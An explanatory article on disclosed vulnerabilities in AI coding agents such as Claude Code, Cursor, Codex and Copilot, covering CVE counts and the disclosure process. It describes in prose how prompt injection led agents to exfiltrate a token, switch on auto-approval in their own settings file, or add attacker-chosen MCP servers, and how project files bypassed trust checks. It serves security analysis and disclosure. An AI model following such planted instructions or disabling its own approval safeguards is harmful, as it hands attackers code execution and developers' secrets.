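# Disclosed vulnerabilities in AI code editors and command-line coding agents

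## What are AI coding agents, and how does a flaw in one become a public record?

A coding agent is a program in which a language model reads a software project, edits its files and runs commands for a developer. Older AI coding tools suggested the next few lines of code, and a person decided whether to keep them. *Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026), a survey of the security research, dates the shift to agents that act on their own to 2024. These agents usually run on the developer's own machine, where they can reach source code, passwords and access keys. Researchers have since disclosed well over a hundred security flaws in such products.

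Some of the products are code editors in which the developer also writes code by hand, such as Cursor, Windsurf and Microsoft's Visual Studio Code (VS Code) with GitHub Copilot. Others run as text in a terminal, such as Anthropic's Claude Code, Google's Gemini CLI and OpenAI's Codex CLI. Windsurf became Devin Desktop on June 2, 2026, but the underlying editor is the same, according to Cognition's *Devin Desktop FAQ*. Gemini CLI stopped serving individual and consumer subscriptions on June 18, and Google now steers those users to its Antigravity products, according to its *Gemini Code Assist consumer accounts*. Companies with a licence keep their access, according to Google's *An important update transitioning Gemini CLI to Antigravity CLI* (2026). Advisories from before June 2026 use the older names.

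The split between editors and terminal tools affects security because editors have many features that predate AI, such as extensions, automatic tasks and settings files that they reload whenever the files change. Cursor and Windsurf are both built on the VS Code codebase, as Real Python's *Devin Desktop* notes for Windsurf, so a risky feature in VS Code can turn up in all three. Some tools fit both categories, such as Codex, which runs the same core program in the terminal and as a VS Code extension.

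### The agent loop

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle at the centre of OpenAI's agent, and the other products work in much the same way. The program first assembles a prompt from the vendor's instructions, a list of available tools, a description of the working environment and the user's request, then sends it to the model. The model returns either a final answer or a request for a tool call, such as listing the files in a folder. The program runs the tool, adds the output to the prompt and sends the whole prompt to the model again. This repeats until the model returns a message with no tool call, which can take hundreds of calls.

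In a typical run described in Anthropic's *How Claude Code works*, an agent asked to fix failing tests might run the tests, read the errors, find, read and edit the relevant files, and then run the tests again. Its tools include the terminal, so it can use any command the developer could type. A developer can add more tools through Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers, which are helper programs often started by a command in a settings file.

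The model does not read or write files itself. It outputs a request, and ordinary software can check the request before carrying it out. The design's weakness is the prompt, where text from a project file or web page can appear alongside the user's own words. According to GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections*, VS Code labels tool output and user messages separately when it sends them, but the server then combines everything into a single text for the model.

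### Prompt injection and the usual attacker

Prompt injection exploits that blending. An attacker plants text in material the model reads, such as a README or an issue (a bug report or request on a project's page), and the model follows it as if the user had written it. In GitHub's security assessment of Copilot, a researcher planted instructions in an issue and then asked the agent what the issue was about. The agent read an access token from a local file and sent it to an outside website without asking the user. Sending private data to a place the attacker can read is called exfiltration. GPT-4.1, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Sonnet 4, all leading models in mid-2025, could each be misled by tool output in these tests.

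Better defences have helped less than their makers hoped. Maloyan and Namiot pooled 78 studies and reported that attacks succeed more than 85% of the time when the attacker adapts to the defence in place. They took their figures from other people's experiments without repeating them, and their literature search ends in December 2025.

Their threat model starts with an attacker who can put content into issues, pull requests (proposed code changes), code comments, documentation or web pages. This attacker cannot alter the vendor's instructions to the model, intercept the conversation between user and agent, or reach the developer's machine except through the agent. Stronger attackers can publish an MCP server or an extension, or tamper with network traffic. Much of the work on coding agents assumes only the weakest attacker, who controls some text or files that the agent will read when the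 developer does something ordinary, like downloading a project and asking a question about it.

### The barriers between a request and its effect

An approval prompt is the question a tool asks the user before it runs a command or changes a protected file. Products differ in which actions need approval. In its default mode, Gemini CLI asks before using most tools that write, according to Google's *Policy engine*. Cursor's agent edits project files without asking but needs approval to edit configuration files, according to Cursor's *Agent Security*. Reviewing an edit afterwards protects the user less than it appears to. GitHub found that when VS Code asked the user whether to keep or undo a change, the changed file was already on disk, and any program watching that file could act on it.

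People also tire of approval prompts and stop reading them. Trend Micro's *GenAI Is Both Hunter and Hunted at Pwn2Own Berlin 2026* (2026), which covers a May 2026 contest where researchers attacked products for prize money, observed that coding agents ask users to accept risks they may be unable to judge. Vendors have responded by having a second model do some of the reviewing. From version 2.1.283, Claude Code starts in a mode where a classifier reviews most actions and blocks the risky ones. Cursor has recommended a similar mode since May 2026, though its *Run Modes* warns that the classifier can block safe actions and allow risky ones.

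An allowlist reduces the questions more simply, by naming commands or web domains that the agent may use without asking, such as the command that runs a project's tests. The software must then check whether each command matches an entry, which is hard because a single line of shell text can hide one command inside another. In Manual mode, Claude Code therefore asks about any command it cannot fully analyse, even if a rule allows part of it. Cursor describes its approval modes, including allowlists, as "best-effort guardrails rather than a hard security boundary".

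The workspace is the project folder in which the agent is meant to work, and most products restrict what the agent may do outside it. The strength of that restriction depends on what enforces it. Anthropic says in its security guide for Claude Code that the Manual-mode boundary is only an approval prompt. File tools need approval to act outside the folder, but an approved shell command can write anywhere the user's account can. Some places inside the folder also need protection. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that Codex makes the `.git` and `.codex` folders read-only by default, even where the agent may write to everything around them.

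A related control, workspace trust, is a setting or dialog that lets a user declare that a folder's contents may run code. In an untrusted folder, Gemini CLI ignores the project's settings, connects to no MCP servers and asks before every tool call. Google's *Trusted Folders* listed the feature as off by default in August 2026, so few Gemini CLI users may see the dialog. Cursor also ships with workspace trust off. Claude Code shows its dialog when a developer starts an interactive session in a new folder. Microsoft's *Secure development with AI in VS Code* warns that once a user trusts a project in VS Code, the project's MCP servers can start without another prompt.

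A sandbox is a set of limits, enforced by the operating system, on what a process may read, write or connect to. OpenAI's *Sandbox* distinguishes the sandbox, which limits what a command can do, from the approval policy, which sets when the agent must stop and ask. A sandbox has the practical advantage that nobody has to interpret the command in advance. If a process inside it tries to write to a forbidden folder, the write fails, however innocent the command looked. Anthropic argues in its sandboxing guide that file limits and network limits are both necessary, because a hijacked agent with open network access could send out the developer's login keys, and one with open file access could tamper with the system until it regained the network.

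Sandboxes do not cover everything an agent does. In Claude Code and Codex, they apply to shell commands. Claude Code's file-editing tools rely on permissions instead, and Codex leaves MCP servers to enforce their own limits. Codex turns off network access for local commands by default, while the Copilot sandbox in VS Code allowed outgoing connections by default in December 2026.

### A harmless example

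Suppose a developer downloads a weather library and asks an agent how to install it. Somebody has added a line to the library's README asking AI assistants to write "pineapple" to `notes.txt` in the folder above the project.

1. The developer opens the project. Workspace trust should act now, by asking whether the folder's contents may run code. In VS Code a refusal also disables the Copilot chat, so the story would end here. The developer accepts.
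2. The agent reads the README. No barrier acts, since reading project files normally needs no approval, and the planted line enters the prompt next to the user's question.
3. The model follows the line and requests an edit to `notes.txt`. The injection has worked, but nothing on the disk has changed.
4. The software compares the file's location with the workspace and finds that it lies outside. It should now show an approval prompt. A developer who asked only about installation has good reason to say no.
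5. The model tries a shell command that would write the same word. The software checks the allowlist, finds no match and should ask again.
6. The developer approves out of habit. If the command runs in a sandbox, the operating system refuses the write. The agent may then ask to run the command outside the sandbox, which gives the developer one more chance to refuse.

If `notes.txt` were moved into the project folder, Cursor and Codex, on their usual settings, would edit it without asking. This does no harm with a plain text file, but a project folder can also hold the agent's own settings and commands that an editor will run.

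### Why a broken check gets a number and a gullible model seldom does

A file is either inside the workspace or outside it, so a check of its location has a right answer. If an oddly written path gets past the check, anyone can reproduce the error, and the vendor can fix the code and say which versions were affected. The GitHub token theft depended on a similar error. VS Code checked web addresses against its list of trusted domains by matching a text pattern instead of parsing each address, so an outside site with a trusted name later in its address passed. The developers separated the agent's web tool from that list and made it ask before fetching a new address.

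The model's tendency to follow planted text is harder to treat this way. Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename* describes an attack in which Copilot followed instructions hidden in a filename. The attack did not work every time, which Tenable attributed to the model's randomness or to other protections. Responsibility is also unclear, because VS Code works with models from several companies, and GitHub lists the underlying confusion of instructions and data among the things the editor cannot control. Microsoft's guide says that instructions guide the model but "aren't an enforcement boundary".

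Not everyone accepts this division. Maloyan and Namiot want the security field to treat prompt injection as its own class of vulnerability and to fix it by changing how agents are architected. Tenable published its finding as an advisory and rated it medium. Randomness is also a weaker reason for the division than it seems, because VS Code ran its models at the setting that makes their answers most consistent, and GitHub noted that this also made attacks easier to reproduce. The better reason is probably that nobody can name a version after which a model stops following planted text. Advisories therefore tend to mention prompt injection as the way in and assign the number to the check that failed afterwards.

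### From private report to public record

Most flaws are first reported privately to the vendor. Cursor, for example, takes reports by email and promises to acknowledge them within five business days. Vendors also learn of flaws through contests. At Pwn2Own Berlin, five teams attacked Codex, four attacked Claude Code and two attacked Cursor. Trend Micro, whose Zero Day Initiative runs the event, withheld the details until the disclosure period had passed. The delay gives the vendor time to reproduce the problem and release a fix before attackers can read about it.

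The vendor may then publish an advisory. Projects hosted on GitHub often use a GitHub advisory, a notice on the project's page with an identifier that begins with GHSA. It normally lists the affected versions and the version that fixes the flaw. A GitHub advisory can exist without a CVE, the public identifier that lets companies and databases refer to the same vulnerability.

CVE Numbering Authorities (CNAs) are organisations authorised to assign CVE numbers and write the records. A record usually describes the flaw and the affected versions. It may also name the type of flaw, using a standard catalogue called the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE). CWE-22, for instance, covers file paths that escape their intended folder. Many records include a severity score from 0 to 10, calculated from a fixed set of judgments about the flaw under the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS).

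The CNA can be the vendor. OpenAI assigns CVE numbers to flaws in its own products, under a policy that covers those discovered outside its standard internal security processes (OpenAI, 2025). A bug that its staff find and fix through those processes need not get a number. Anthropic became a CNA on July 28, 2026, according to *Anthropic’s CNA Designation Marks the Industrialization of Vulnerability Discovery* (Callahan, 2026). A vendor that is not a CNA can get numbers from another one, such as GitHub, which assigns them for many projects it hosts.

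The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) sponsors the CVE Program, which the non-profit MITRE operates. CISA also keeps a separate catalogue of flaws that attackers are known to have used. Infosecurity Magazine's *AI Companies to Play Bigger Role in CVE Program, Says CISA* reported that CISA wants AI companies to take a larger part in the programme. One reason, according to a document on the CVE Program's *Frontier AI Researcher CVE Numbering Authorities (CNAs) Pilot*, is that these companies may find flaws faster than the existing process can handle them.

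The National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) runs the National Vulnerability Database (NVD), which lists CVE records and adds its own details. NIST used to try to analyse every CVE and supply a severity score and a list of affected products. In April 2026 it announced that, because of the growing volume, it would do this only for CVEs that meet certain criteria. The Hacker News (2026) reported that NIST processed nearly 42,000 CVEs in 2025, 45% more than in any earlier year, and that submissions in the first three months of 2026 were up by almost a third.

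The remaining CVEs stay in the database under the label "Not Scheduled". According to SiliconANGLE (2026), that group includes the unprocessed backlog from before March 1, 2026, except for flaws that CISA lists as known to have been exploited. Users can email NIST to request an analysis. NIST has also stopped routinely adding its own severity score when the CNA has already supplied one, so when a vendor assigns CVE numbers to flaws in its own coding agent, the vendor's score may be the only one a reader finds.

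## How many vulnerabilities have been disclosed, and how many never got a number?

A CVE record names a vendor and a product but doesn't mark the product as a coding agent, so there is no official total for these tools. The figure of more than a hundred disclosed flaws comes from adding up counts for individual products. The share with a CVE number varies widely between sources. In July 2026, 29 of the 30 advisories on Claude Code's GitHub page had one, while *Bad Vibes* lists CVE numbers for only 17 of the 81 reports that Ashkenazi and Tsukerman made about 22 products.

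### The record by year

Few vulnerabilities are on record for 2024, partly because few coding agents existed yet. One, CVE-2024-48919, affected Terminal Cmd-K, a Cursor feature that wrote terminal commands at the user's request. According to NVD's *CVE-2024-48919 Detail*, if the user included a web page in the request, an attacker who controlled that page had a significant chance of making the model write a command of the attacker's choosing. The flaw affected Cursor before September 27, 2024, and GCVE (2024), a vulnerability database, dates the public record to October 22.

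That record's title describes the flaw as remote code execution (RCE), which means that an attacker with no prior access to the victim's machine can run code on it. Unusually, the title also gives prompt injection as the cause. The danger was limited because the user had to import the hostile page deliberately. Agents that open files and web pages on their own don't require that step.

Disclosures rose from the middle of 2025. Anthropic set up Claude Code's GitHub project in February 2025, published the project's first advisory on June 23, and had published 13 by December. Late that year, the IDEsaster research project produced 24 CVEs across several products. Anthropic published 17 more advisories in the first half of 2026. New products and a growing number of researchers explain at least part of this rise, so it does not show that the software was getting worse.

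송 (2026) reports in *클로드 코드·코덱스·커서 등 AI 에이전트 8건 결함, .git 설정으로 명령 몰래 실행* that by early September the security firm Manifold Security had described eight flaws, four of them unresolved, in seven command-line agents, and OpenAI had three separate CVEs for Codex. Another Claude Code flaw, CVE-2026-88968, became public in November.

### Thirty advisories for Claude Code

Claude Code's disclosed vulnerabilities are the easiest to count because Anthropic publishes its advisories on one page. A copy of that page from July 21, 2026, kept by the GitHub viewer goard, lists 30 advisories. Anthropic rated 24 of them high severity, four moderate and two low. They fall into seven groups according to what went wrong.

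| What went wrong | 2025 | 2026 | Severity |
|---|---|---|---|
| A shell command got past the check that should have stopped it or asked the user | 5 | 4 | 9 high |
| A project's code or settings took effect without the user's informed trust | 5 | 3 | 7 high, 1 moderate |
| Code got out of the sandbox | 0 | 3 | 3 high |
| A file path or symlink got around a restriction on files | 2 | 1 | 1 high, 2 low |
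| The agent could contact an unsafe web address without asking | 0 | 2 | 1 high, 1 moderate |
| The software accepted a connection it should have refused | 1 | 1 | 2 high |
| Another user of the same computer could interfere | 0 | 3 | 1 high, 2 moderate |
| Total | 13 | 17 | 24 high, 4 moderate, 2 low |

A symlink is a file system entry that points to another path, so a write to the symlink lands at that path. Some flaws could fit in more than one row. For example, CVE-2026-24053 was an error in reading a shell command, but it allowed writes outside the workspace.

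Over half of the advisories belong to the first two groups, command-check flaws and trust flaws. To exploit most command-check flaws, an attacker had to plant text that the model would read. Most trust flaws needed no prompt injection, because the attacker's code or settings took effect as Claude Code started. In CVE-2025-59041, for instance, Claude Code ran a command at startup that included the user's Git email address. A malicious address could run code before the user answered the trust dialog, according to stack.watch's *Anthropic Claude Code*.

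A few of the advisories describe flaws that could occur in a program with no AI. According to GitLab's advisory database, an attacker exploiting the June 2026 flaw in the `/copy` command needed an account on the same computer and had to wait for a more privileged user to run the command. Two others concern Claude Desktop, the graphical app for running Claude Code sessions. One was in the app's remote-connection feature, which checked that it recognized a server's name but not that the server's key matched the stored one.

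The one advisory without a CVE number concerns the wording of Claude Code's trust dialog, which did not make clear that accepting it would let the program execute the folder's files without asking again. According to GitLab, Anthropic rated the problem high severity and rewrote the warning.

CVE-2026-88968 brings the count to at least 31. According to rulestack (2026), who writes about Claude Code's settings on DEV Community, it affects versions below 2.1.251 on macOS, where code inside the sandbox could redirect a file edit outside the workspace. In *Breaking the Workspace Boundary*, Jha describes a very similar attack under a report number from HackerOne, a service through which researchers submit bugs to companies. The two accounts may describe the same flaw, so including both in a total could count it twice.

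### Why trackers give other totals

Several websites collect vulnerability records by product, and their totals for Claude Code range from 20 to 34. In June 2026, stack.watch listed 29 CVEs. Anthropic's page listed the same number a month later, but only 26 appear on both lists. Stack.watch did not yet have three that Anthropic disclosed in June, and it included three from April that are not on Anthropic's page.

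Anthropic did not publish those three April records itself. *Anthropic Claude Code & Agent SDK OS Command Injection via Authentication Helper*, from the security firm VulnCheck, describes the most severe, CVE-2026-35022, and rates it critical, at 9.3 out of 10. A Claude Code settings file can specify a helper command that fetches login details. Claude Code passed that command to the shell without checking it, so anyone who could change the setting could run other commands. A reader who relied on Anthropic's page alone would miss this flaw.

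CVEs for one product can also be listed under different names. RadicalNotion.AI lists 34 CVEs under *Anthropics claude-code Vulnerabilities*, with the vendor spelled as in the company's GitHub account, and 26 under *Anthropic claude code Vulnerabilities*. The lists may overlap, so their sum is not a reliable total. Neither list contains a flaw from CISA's catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities.

Other trackers count only the package that developers install through npm, a distribution service for JavaScript software. Corgea's *@anthropic-ai/claude-code* lists 27 advisories. Ecosyste.ms' *Security Advisories for @anthropic-ai/claude-code in npm* lists 20, the latest from February 2026. Duplicates, by contrast, can raise a total. GitLab's *GHSA-9f65-56v6-gxw7* (2025) contains only a note that it duplicates another advisory, yet it has its own identifier.

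Trackers also disagree about Anthropic's related products. In October 2026, Security NEXT's *「Claude Agent SDK」に引数注入の脆弱性* (2026) reported CVE-2026-96620 in the Claude Agent SDK, a kit for building other programs on the agent behind Claude Code. An attacker who could choose the ID of the session to resume could add options to Claude Code's command line and so run commands. Whether this counts as a Claude Code flaw depends on how the tracker defines the product.

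Trackers' descriptions also need checking. vuln.today's page *Claude Code* listed 25 CVEs in October 2026, seven fewer than if it had included all of Anthropic's July list. The page attributes CVE-2026-25722 to malicious MCP servers, but the description reproduced on stack.watch concerns a command that changes folder before writing a file. It also lists no available patch for CVE-2026-24887, which Anthropic fixed in version 2.0.72.

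### The "Bad Vibes" study

A vendor's page shows only what the vendor chose to publish. Ashkenazi and Tsukerman, two researchers at the security company Palo Alto Networks, instead started their count from the flaws they had reported. They presented the results at the Black Hat Asia conference in 2026.

The researchers divide an attack into three stages: reaching the model, getting past its guardrails and causing harm. They concentrate on the third stage, assuming that a prompt injection has already worked and testing whether the software around the model stops what follows. They tried the same few kinds of attack on many products and sorted the results into three groups.

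- **Command injection:** The attacker hides a forbidden command inside one that the agent may run without asking. The researchers often used the computer's calculator as the hidden program, since its appearance on the screen proves that the command ran.
- **File-system flaws:** The agent writes outside the workspace, or changes a protected settings file inside it.
- **Sandbox escapes:** The attacker can already run any code inside the sandbox and finds a way to affect the rest of the machine.

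The table below combines their results by product. Each cell gives the number of reports, with the number of CVEs in brackets.

| Product | Command injection | File system | Sandbox escape | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 4 (2) | 6 (0) | 4 (1) | 14 (3) |
| Cursor | 3 (0) | 8 (3) | 2 (0) | 13 (3) |
| Codex | 1 (0) | 6 (0) | 3 (0) | 10 (0) |
| Kiro (Amazon) | 4 (0) | 5 (0) | – | 9 (0) |
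| Gemini CLI | 2 (0) | 2 (0) | 2 (0) | 6 (0) |
| Antigravity (Google) | – | 3 (0) | 2 (0) | 5 (0) |
| Copilot in VS Code | 1 (0) | 2 (1) | – | 3 (1) |
| Windsurf | – | 3 (0) | – | 3 (0) |
| 14 other products | 11 (5) | 7 (5) | – | 18 (10) |
| Total | 26 (7) | 42 (9) | 13 (1) | 81 (17) |

Two of the researchers' own totals are one higher than these sums. They give 43 file-system reports where their rows add up to 42, and 18 CVEs where their three groups add up to 17. Their overall figure of "81+ reports before we stopped counting" matches the sum of the rows.

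Ten of the 17 CVEs were still reserved, meaning their numbers had been set aside but their records were not yet public. A search of the public databases at that time would have found only the other seven, about one for every twelve reports.

All ten reserved CVE numbers belong to the 14 products in the last row. Those products had 18 reports and ten CVE numbers, while the eight products listed above them had 63 reports and seven CVE numbers. Cline, a small coding agent, had a CVE for each of its two reports, while Codex had none for its ten. The attacks were the same kinds, so differences in vendors' practices probably explain much of the gap.

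These figures also give a rough minimum of 102 for the whole field. That total includes Anthropic's 30 advisories, the 67 "Bad Vibes" reports on products other than Claude Code, the three April CVEs, Cursor's 2024 flaw and CVE-2026-88968. IDEsaster and Manifold Security's findings would raise it, though some may overlap with the reports already counted.

### Do few CVEs mean few flaws?

Ashkenazi and Tsukerman conclude that a coding agent with few CVEs probably still has vulnerabilities. Their results for Codex, Kiro and Gemini CLI support this, since 25 reports across the three products led to no CVEs. They also found each type of flaw in many products. In September 2026, The Information's *Same Flaw Found in Claude Code, Codex, Gemini CLI and GitHub Copilot* reported another case of competing agents sharing a weakness.

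However, a report is not necessarily a confirmed flaw. The researchers acknowledge that not everyone considers the results of a prompt injection severe, and their figures do not separate the reports that vendors accepted from those they rejected. Two reports can also lead to one fix and one CVE. Some CVEs are missing only because they take time to assign, since the researchers found that most large vendors fix bugs quickly but assign CVEs slowly. The count of zero for Codex was out of date by September, when 송 counted three CVEs.

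Still, the researchers received many more fixes and acknowledgements than CVEs, so a good part of the unnumbered reports described real problems. Other flaws may have even less of a public record. In October 2026, the security firm Pillar Security said the makers of OpenCode, another coding agent, had fixed a critical RCE flaw without telling users (Poireault, 2026, *Researchers Warn OpenCode Quietly Patched Critical RCE Flaw*).

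A short list of CVEs is therefore not evidence that a product is safe. The evidence also does not show that all the products have about the same number of flaws, because nobody examined them all with equal effort. For the same reason, Claude Code's long list does not show that it is the least safe agent. The list may be long partly because Anthropic publishes more of what it fixes.

### What happened at Pwn2Own Berlin

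The Pwn2Own contest of May 2026 offers a separate check, because entrants had to make their attacks work on stage within a time limit. *Pwn2Own Berlin 2026* (Childs, 2026) gives the daily results and distinguishes wins from collisions. A collision is a working attack that relies on a bug the vendor or the organisers already know about, so it usually earns less.

| Product | Entries | Wins | Collisions | Failures | Prize money |
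|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex | 5 | 3 | 1 | 1 | $90,000 |
| Claude Code | 3 | 0 | 3 | 0 | $60,000 |
| Claude Desktop | 1 | 0 | 1 | 0 | $10,000 |
| Cursor | 2 | 2 | 0 | 0 | $45,000 |

Ten of the 11 attacks worked. In the other, Le Duc Anh Vu of Viettel Cyber Security ran out of time against Codex on the first day, before succeeding against Cursor on the second. Compass Security won the largest single prize in the category, $40,000, for attacking Codex with one CWE-150 bug, a type of flaw in which a program fails to neutralise special control characters in its input. Childs lists Compass Security again on the third day, when its attack on Claude Code collided with an earlier one. In the daily results, Compass Security is also credited with the second win against Cursor, but Trend Micro names STARLabs in its later review.

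"Bad Vibes" listed no CVEs for Codex, yet four of five entrants broke it, which agrees with the paper's conclusion. The results for Claude Code are harder to interpret because every attack worked but nobody won outright. Anthropic already knew about the bug that Viettel used on the first day, and OpenAI already knew about the bug behind the Codex collision. A vendor can therefore know about a flaw that is still exploitable and does not appear in any public count.

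The number of entries is a poor measure of which agent is weakest, because Trend Micro received a record number of submissions and had to choose among them. Apart from the Claude Desktop entry, the only targets in the category were Claude Code, Codex and Cursor, so the contest provides no comparison with Copilot or Gemini CLI.

### Flaws in software that AI wrote

Headlines about AI coding tools and CVEs often refer to vulnerabilities in software built with these tools, rather than in the tools themselves. Researchers at Georgia Tech track such cases in a project called Vibe Security Radar. They find the change that fixed a published vulnerability, then trace the code back to the change that introduced it. If that change has an AI tool's signature, AI agents investigate whether the generated code contributed to the flaw.

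By March 2026 the project had confirmed 74 cases, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Researchers Sound the Alarm on Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code* (2026). At least 35 of the CVEs came out in March, up from 15 in February and six in January. Hanqing Zhao, the project's founder, estimated the true number at five to ten times the number detected, because many developers remove the signatures and some tools never leave any.

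Claude Code also appears most often in that count, but as the tool that helped write the faulty code. Zhao attributes its lead mostly to Claude Code always signing its work. These flaws put users of the finished programs at risk, and updating Claude Code would not fix them.

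## What happens when an agent can edit its own settings?

Coding agents usually keep their settings in a plain text file. One setting controls whether the agent must ask before running a command, another lists the commands it may run without asking, and a third names the MCP servers to start. In many products, this file is in the project folder, where the agent can write. An attacker who plants text that the model reads then needs the agent to make only one unapproved edit to the file. That edit can turn off all later approval prompts or add an MCP server whose start command the attacker chose.

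The software treats an agent's edit to its own settings file like any other edit, since changing project files is the agent's normal work. The damage comes a moment later, when the program rereads the file and applies the new rules. In the summer of 2025, researchers reported versions of this flaw in GitHub Copilot, Amp, Cursor and Amazon's Kiro.

### GitHub Copilot and the auto-approve setting

Johann Rehberger, who writes the security blog Embrace The Red, reported the Copilot flaw to Microsoft on June 29, 2025. Rehberger had noticed that Copilot's agent in VS Code could create and change project files without approval, and looked for a project setting that would make this dangerous. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot* describes the resulting attack, now CVE-2025-53773.

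1. A developer asks Copilot about a source file that contains planted instructions. The text could also come from a web page, a GitHub issue or the output of an MCP server.
2. The model follows the instructions and requests an edit to `.vscode/settings.json`, which holds the project's VS Code settings. If the file doesn't exist, the agent creates it.
3. The edit sets `chat.tools.autoApprove` to true. This option turned off every confirmation. Microsoft called it experimental, but ordinary installations of VS Code included it.
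4. VS Code applies the new setting immediately.
5. The model requests a terminal command, and VS Code runs it without asking.

Rehberger's demonstration opened the calculator on Windows and macOS. It also worked with instructions written in invisible characters, though less reliably, and models often refused to follow them.

The agent's change to its settings took effect at once because VS Code saved the agent's edits before the user reviewed them and reloaded the settings whenever the file changed. GitHub said the immediate saving was deliberate because the agent works through several files step by step.

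GitHub's own researcher used the same behaviour by planting an issue with instructions for the agent to edit the user's personal VS Code settings, which lie outside the project, and replace the command that starts the GitHub MCP server. VS Code reloaded the server's configuration and ran the new command before the researcher could review the edit. Markus Vervier of Persistent Security and Ari Marzuk also found the underlying flaw independently, and Microsoft told Rehberger that it was already tracking the problem.

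### What Microsoft changed

Microsoft published the CVE on August 12, 2025, and Rehberger wrote that the August update fixed the flaw. The CVE record, MITRE's *GitHub Copilot and Visual Studio Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* (2025), describes the command injection in only one sentence and gives a severity score of 7.8. It lists only Visual Studio 2022 as affected, from version 17.14.0 up to but not including 17.14.12. Visual Studio is a separate program from VS Code, where Rehberger demonstrated the attack, so a VS Code user can't learn from the record which version is safe.

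Later in August, GitHub reported that VS Code no longer let the agent edit files outside the workspace. This change blocked the GitHub researcher's attack but would not have blocked Rehberger's, because `.vscode/settings.json` is inside the workspace. At the time, a confirmation step for configuration files was available only in the preview edition of VS Code.

A step that makes the agent ask before it edits files outside the workspace, common system folders or dotfiles reached all users on September 11, according to Microsoft's *August 2025 (version 1.104)* (2025). Dotfiles are files and folders whose names begin with a dot, and they often hold settings. Microsoft also renamed the auto-approve option to `chat.tools.global.autoApprove` and did not carry over old values, so anyone who had turned it on, knowingly or not, had to do so again. The option now shows a warning on first use. Microsoft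 had found that people were enabling it without thinking hard about the consequences, and that some wrongly believed they needed it to approve terminal commands automatically.

On November 11 Microsoft disclosed CVE-2025-62222, a gap in the new guard that still let a hijacked agent write to `.vscode/settings.json`. According to GitHub's *Sensitive file editing guard bypass* (2025), version 0.32.5 of the Copilot Chat extension closed the gap by guarding the creation of new files in the same way as changes to existing ones. Rehberger had already mentioned, when describing the original attack, that the agent would create the settings file if it was missing.

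### Amp and Kiro

A few days before publishing the Copilot attack, Rehberger disclosed a similar one in Amp, a coding agent then built by Sourcegraph. Amp kept its allowlist and its MCP servers in the user's personal VS Code settings. Embrace The Red's *Amp Code* describes this as normally a good choice, because most agents can work only inside the project folder. But Amp could write anywhere in the user's files without approval.

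An attacker could therefore plant text that told the agent to add commands to the allowlist, or a wildcard that covered every command, and then run them. The text could also tell the agent to add an MCP server, which Amp started immediately. Rehberger demonstrated this by putting the instructions in a comment in a small C program and asking Amp about the file. Sourcegraph fixed the flaw within days of the report in July.

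Kiro had the same weakness. AWS, Amazon's cloud division, fixed it in version 0.1.42 by August 5, 2025, without issuing a CVE, according to Embrace The Red's *AWS Kiro*.

Two related flaws in Kiro became public in 2026. In June, AWS's *CVE-2026-10591* (2026) announced that versions before 0.11 let the agent write to files such as `.vscode/tasks.json`, which can hold commands that the editor runs when someone opens the folder. In July, Intezer (2026) described how Kiro could rewrite the MCP settings file in the user's home folder. Kiro reloaded the file after each change and started the servers it listed. Smith reports in *AWS Kiro Flaw Turned Hidden Web Text Into Code Execution* that the planted text could be hidden in a web page that the agent fetched, and that AWS has released a fix.

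The repeated vulnerabilities suggest that fixing one file or one attack route at a time leaves others open. Intezer blames Kiro's reliance on a person to approve risky actions and argues that the platform itself should protect these files.

### Two flaws in Cursor's MCP settings

Two Cursor vulnerabilities that became public within days of each other in August 2025 both end with Cursor starting an MCP server that runs an attacker's command. In CurXecute (CVE-2025-54135), the agent writes a new server entry, while in MCPoison (CVE-2025-54136), someone alters an entry the user has already approved.

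*When Public Prompts Turn Into Local Shells* (Abu, 2025) gives an example of CurXecute in which a developer has connected Cursor to Slack through an MCP server. An attacker posts a message in a public Slack channel. When the agent fetches the message, the model follows the instructions in it and proposes adding a server to `mcp.json`, the file that lists Cursor's MCP servers. Cursor saved the edit to disk and started the new server immediately, so the attacker's command ran even if the developer then rejected the edit.

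According to GCVE (2025), Cursor's agent needed approval to edit an existing dotfile but not to create one. A project without an MCP settings file was therefore easier to attack than a project with one. Microsoft's safeguard had the same gap three months later.

Accounts of CurXecute differ on where the rewritten file is and which version fixed the flaw. Abu places the file in the user's home folder, where it applies to all projects, while the CVE record describes a file in the workspace. Abu gives the fixed version as 1.3, and GCVE gives 1.3.9, which is safer to rely on. Cursor's developers merged a patch on July 8, one day after the report. The CVE record does not describe the patch, but the error it describes implies that creating a protected file now needs approval, as editing one already did.

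The MCPoison attack on Cursor needs no prompt injection. In *CVE-2025-54136*, Charikov, Zaikin and Vanunu (2025), researchers at the security company Check Point, found that Cursor asked the user to approve each new MCP entry in a project but stored the approval only under the entry's name. An attacker could add an entry with a harmless command to a shared project, wait for a colleague to approve it, and then replace the command while keeping the name. Cursor ran the new command without asking each time the colleague opened the project.

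The attacker here needs more access than in CurXecute. MITRE's *Cursor's Modification of MCP Server Definitions Bypasses Manual Re-approvals* (2025) specifies either permission to change a branch the victim is using or the ability to write files on the victim's machine. But the attacker doesn't have to get a model to do anything, and the access lasts until somebody notices the changed entry.

Cursor fixed MCPoison in version 1.3, released on July 29, 2025. The release notes did not mention the flaw, so Charikov and colleagues tested the new version. They found that any change to an MCP entry, even an added space, triggered a new approval prompt. The likely fix for CurXecute would not have stopped MCPoison, because restricting what the agent may create does not affect a file that arrives through Git.

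### Codex CLI: settings supplied by the project

In CVE-2025-61260, a vulnerability in Codex CLI, the attacker's settings come with the project, and the agent does not write any settings itself. Neither the model nor the user makes a mistake that a better prompt could have prevented.

Codex reads its settings, including its list of MCP servers, from a folder that normally belongs to the user, but the `CODEX_HOME` variable can point it to another folder. Mill and Vanunu (2025), in *CVE-2025-61260 — OpenAI Codex CLI*, showed that Codex also accepted this variable from a project's `.env` file, where developers commonly keep the project's variables. A malicious project could therefore use its `.env` file to point Codex to a settings folder inside the project. When a developer ran `codex` in that project, the program loaded those settings at startup and ran each listed MCP server's start command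 without an approval prompt.

Codex treated whatever settings folder it ended up with as the user's own, but a `.env` file could move that folder into a project. OpenAI blocked this in version 0.23.0, released on August 20, 2025, 13 days after Check Point's report.

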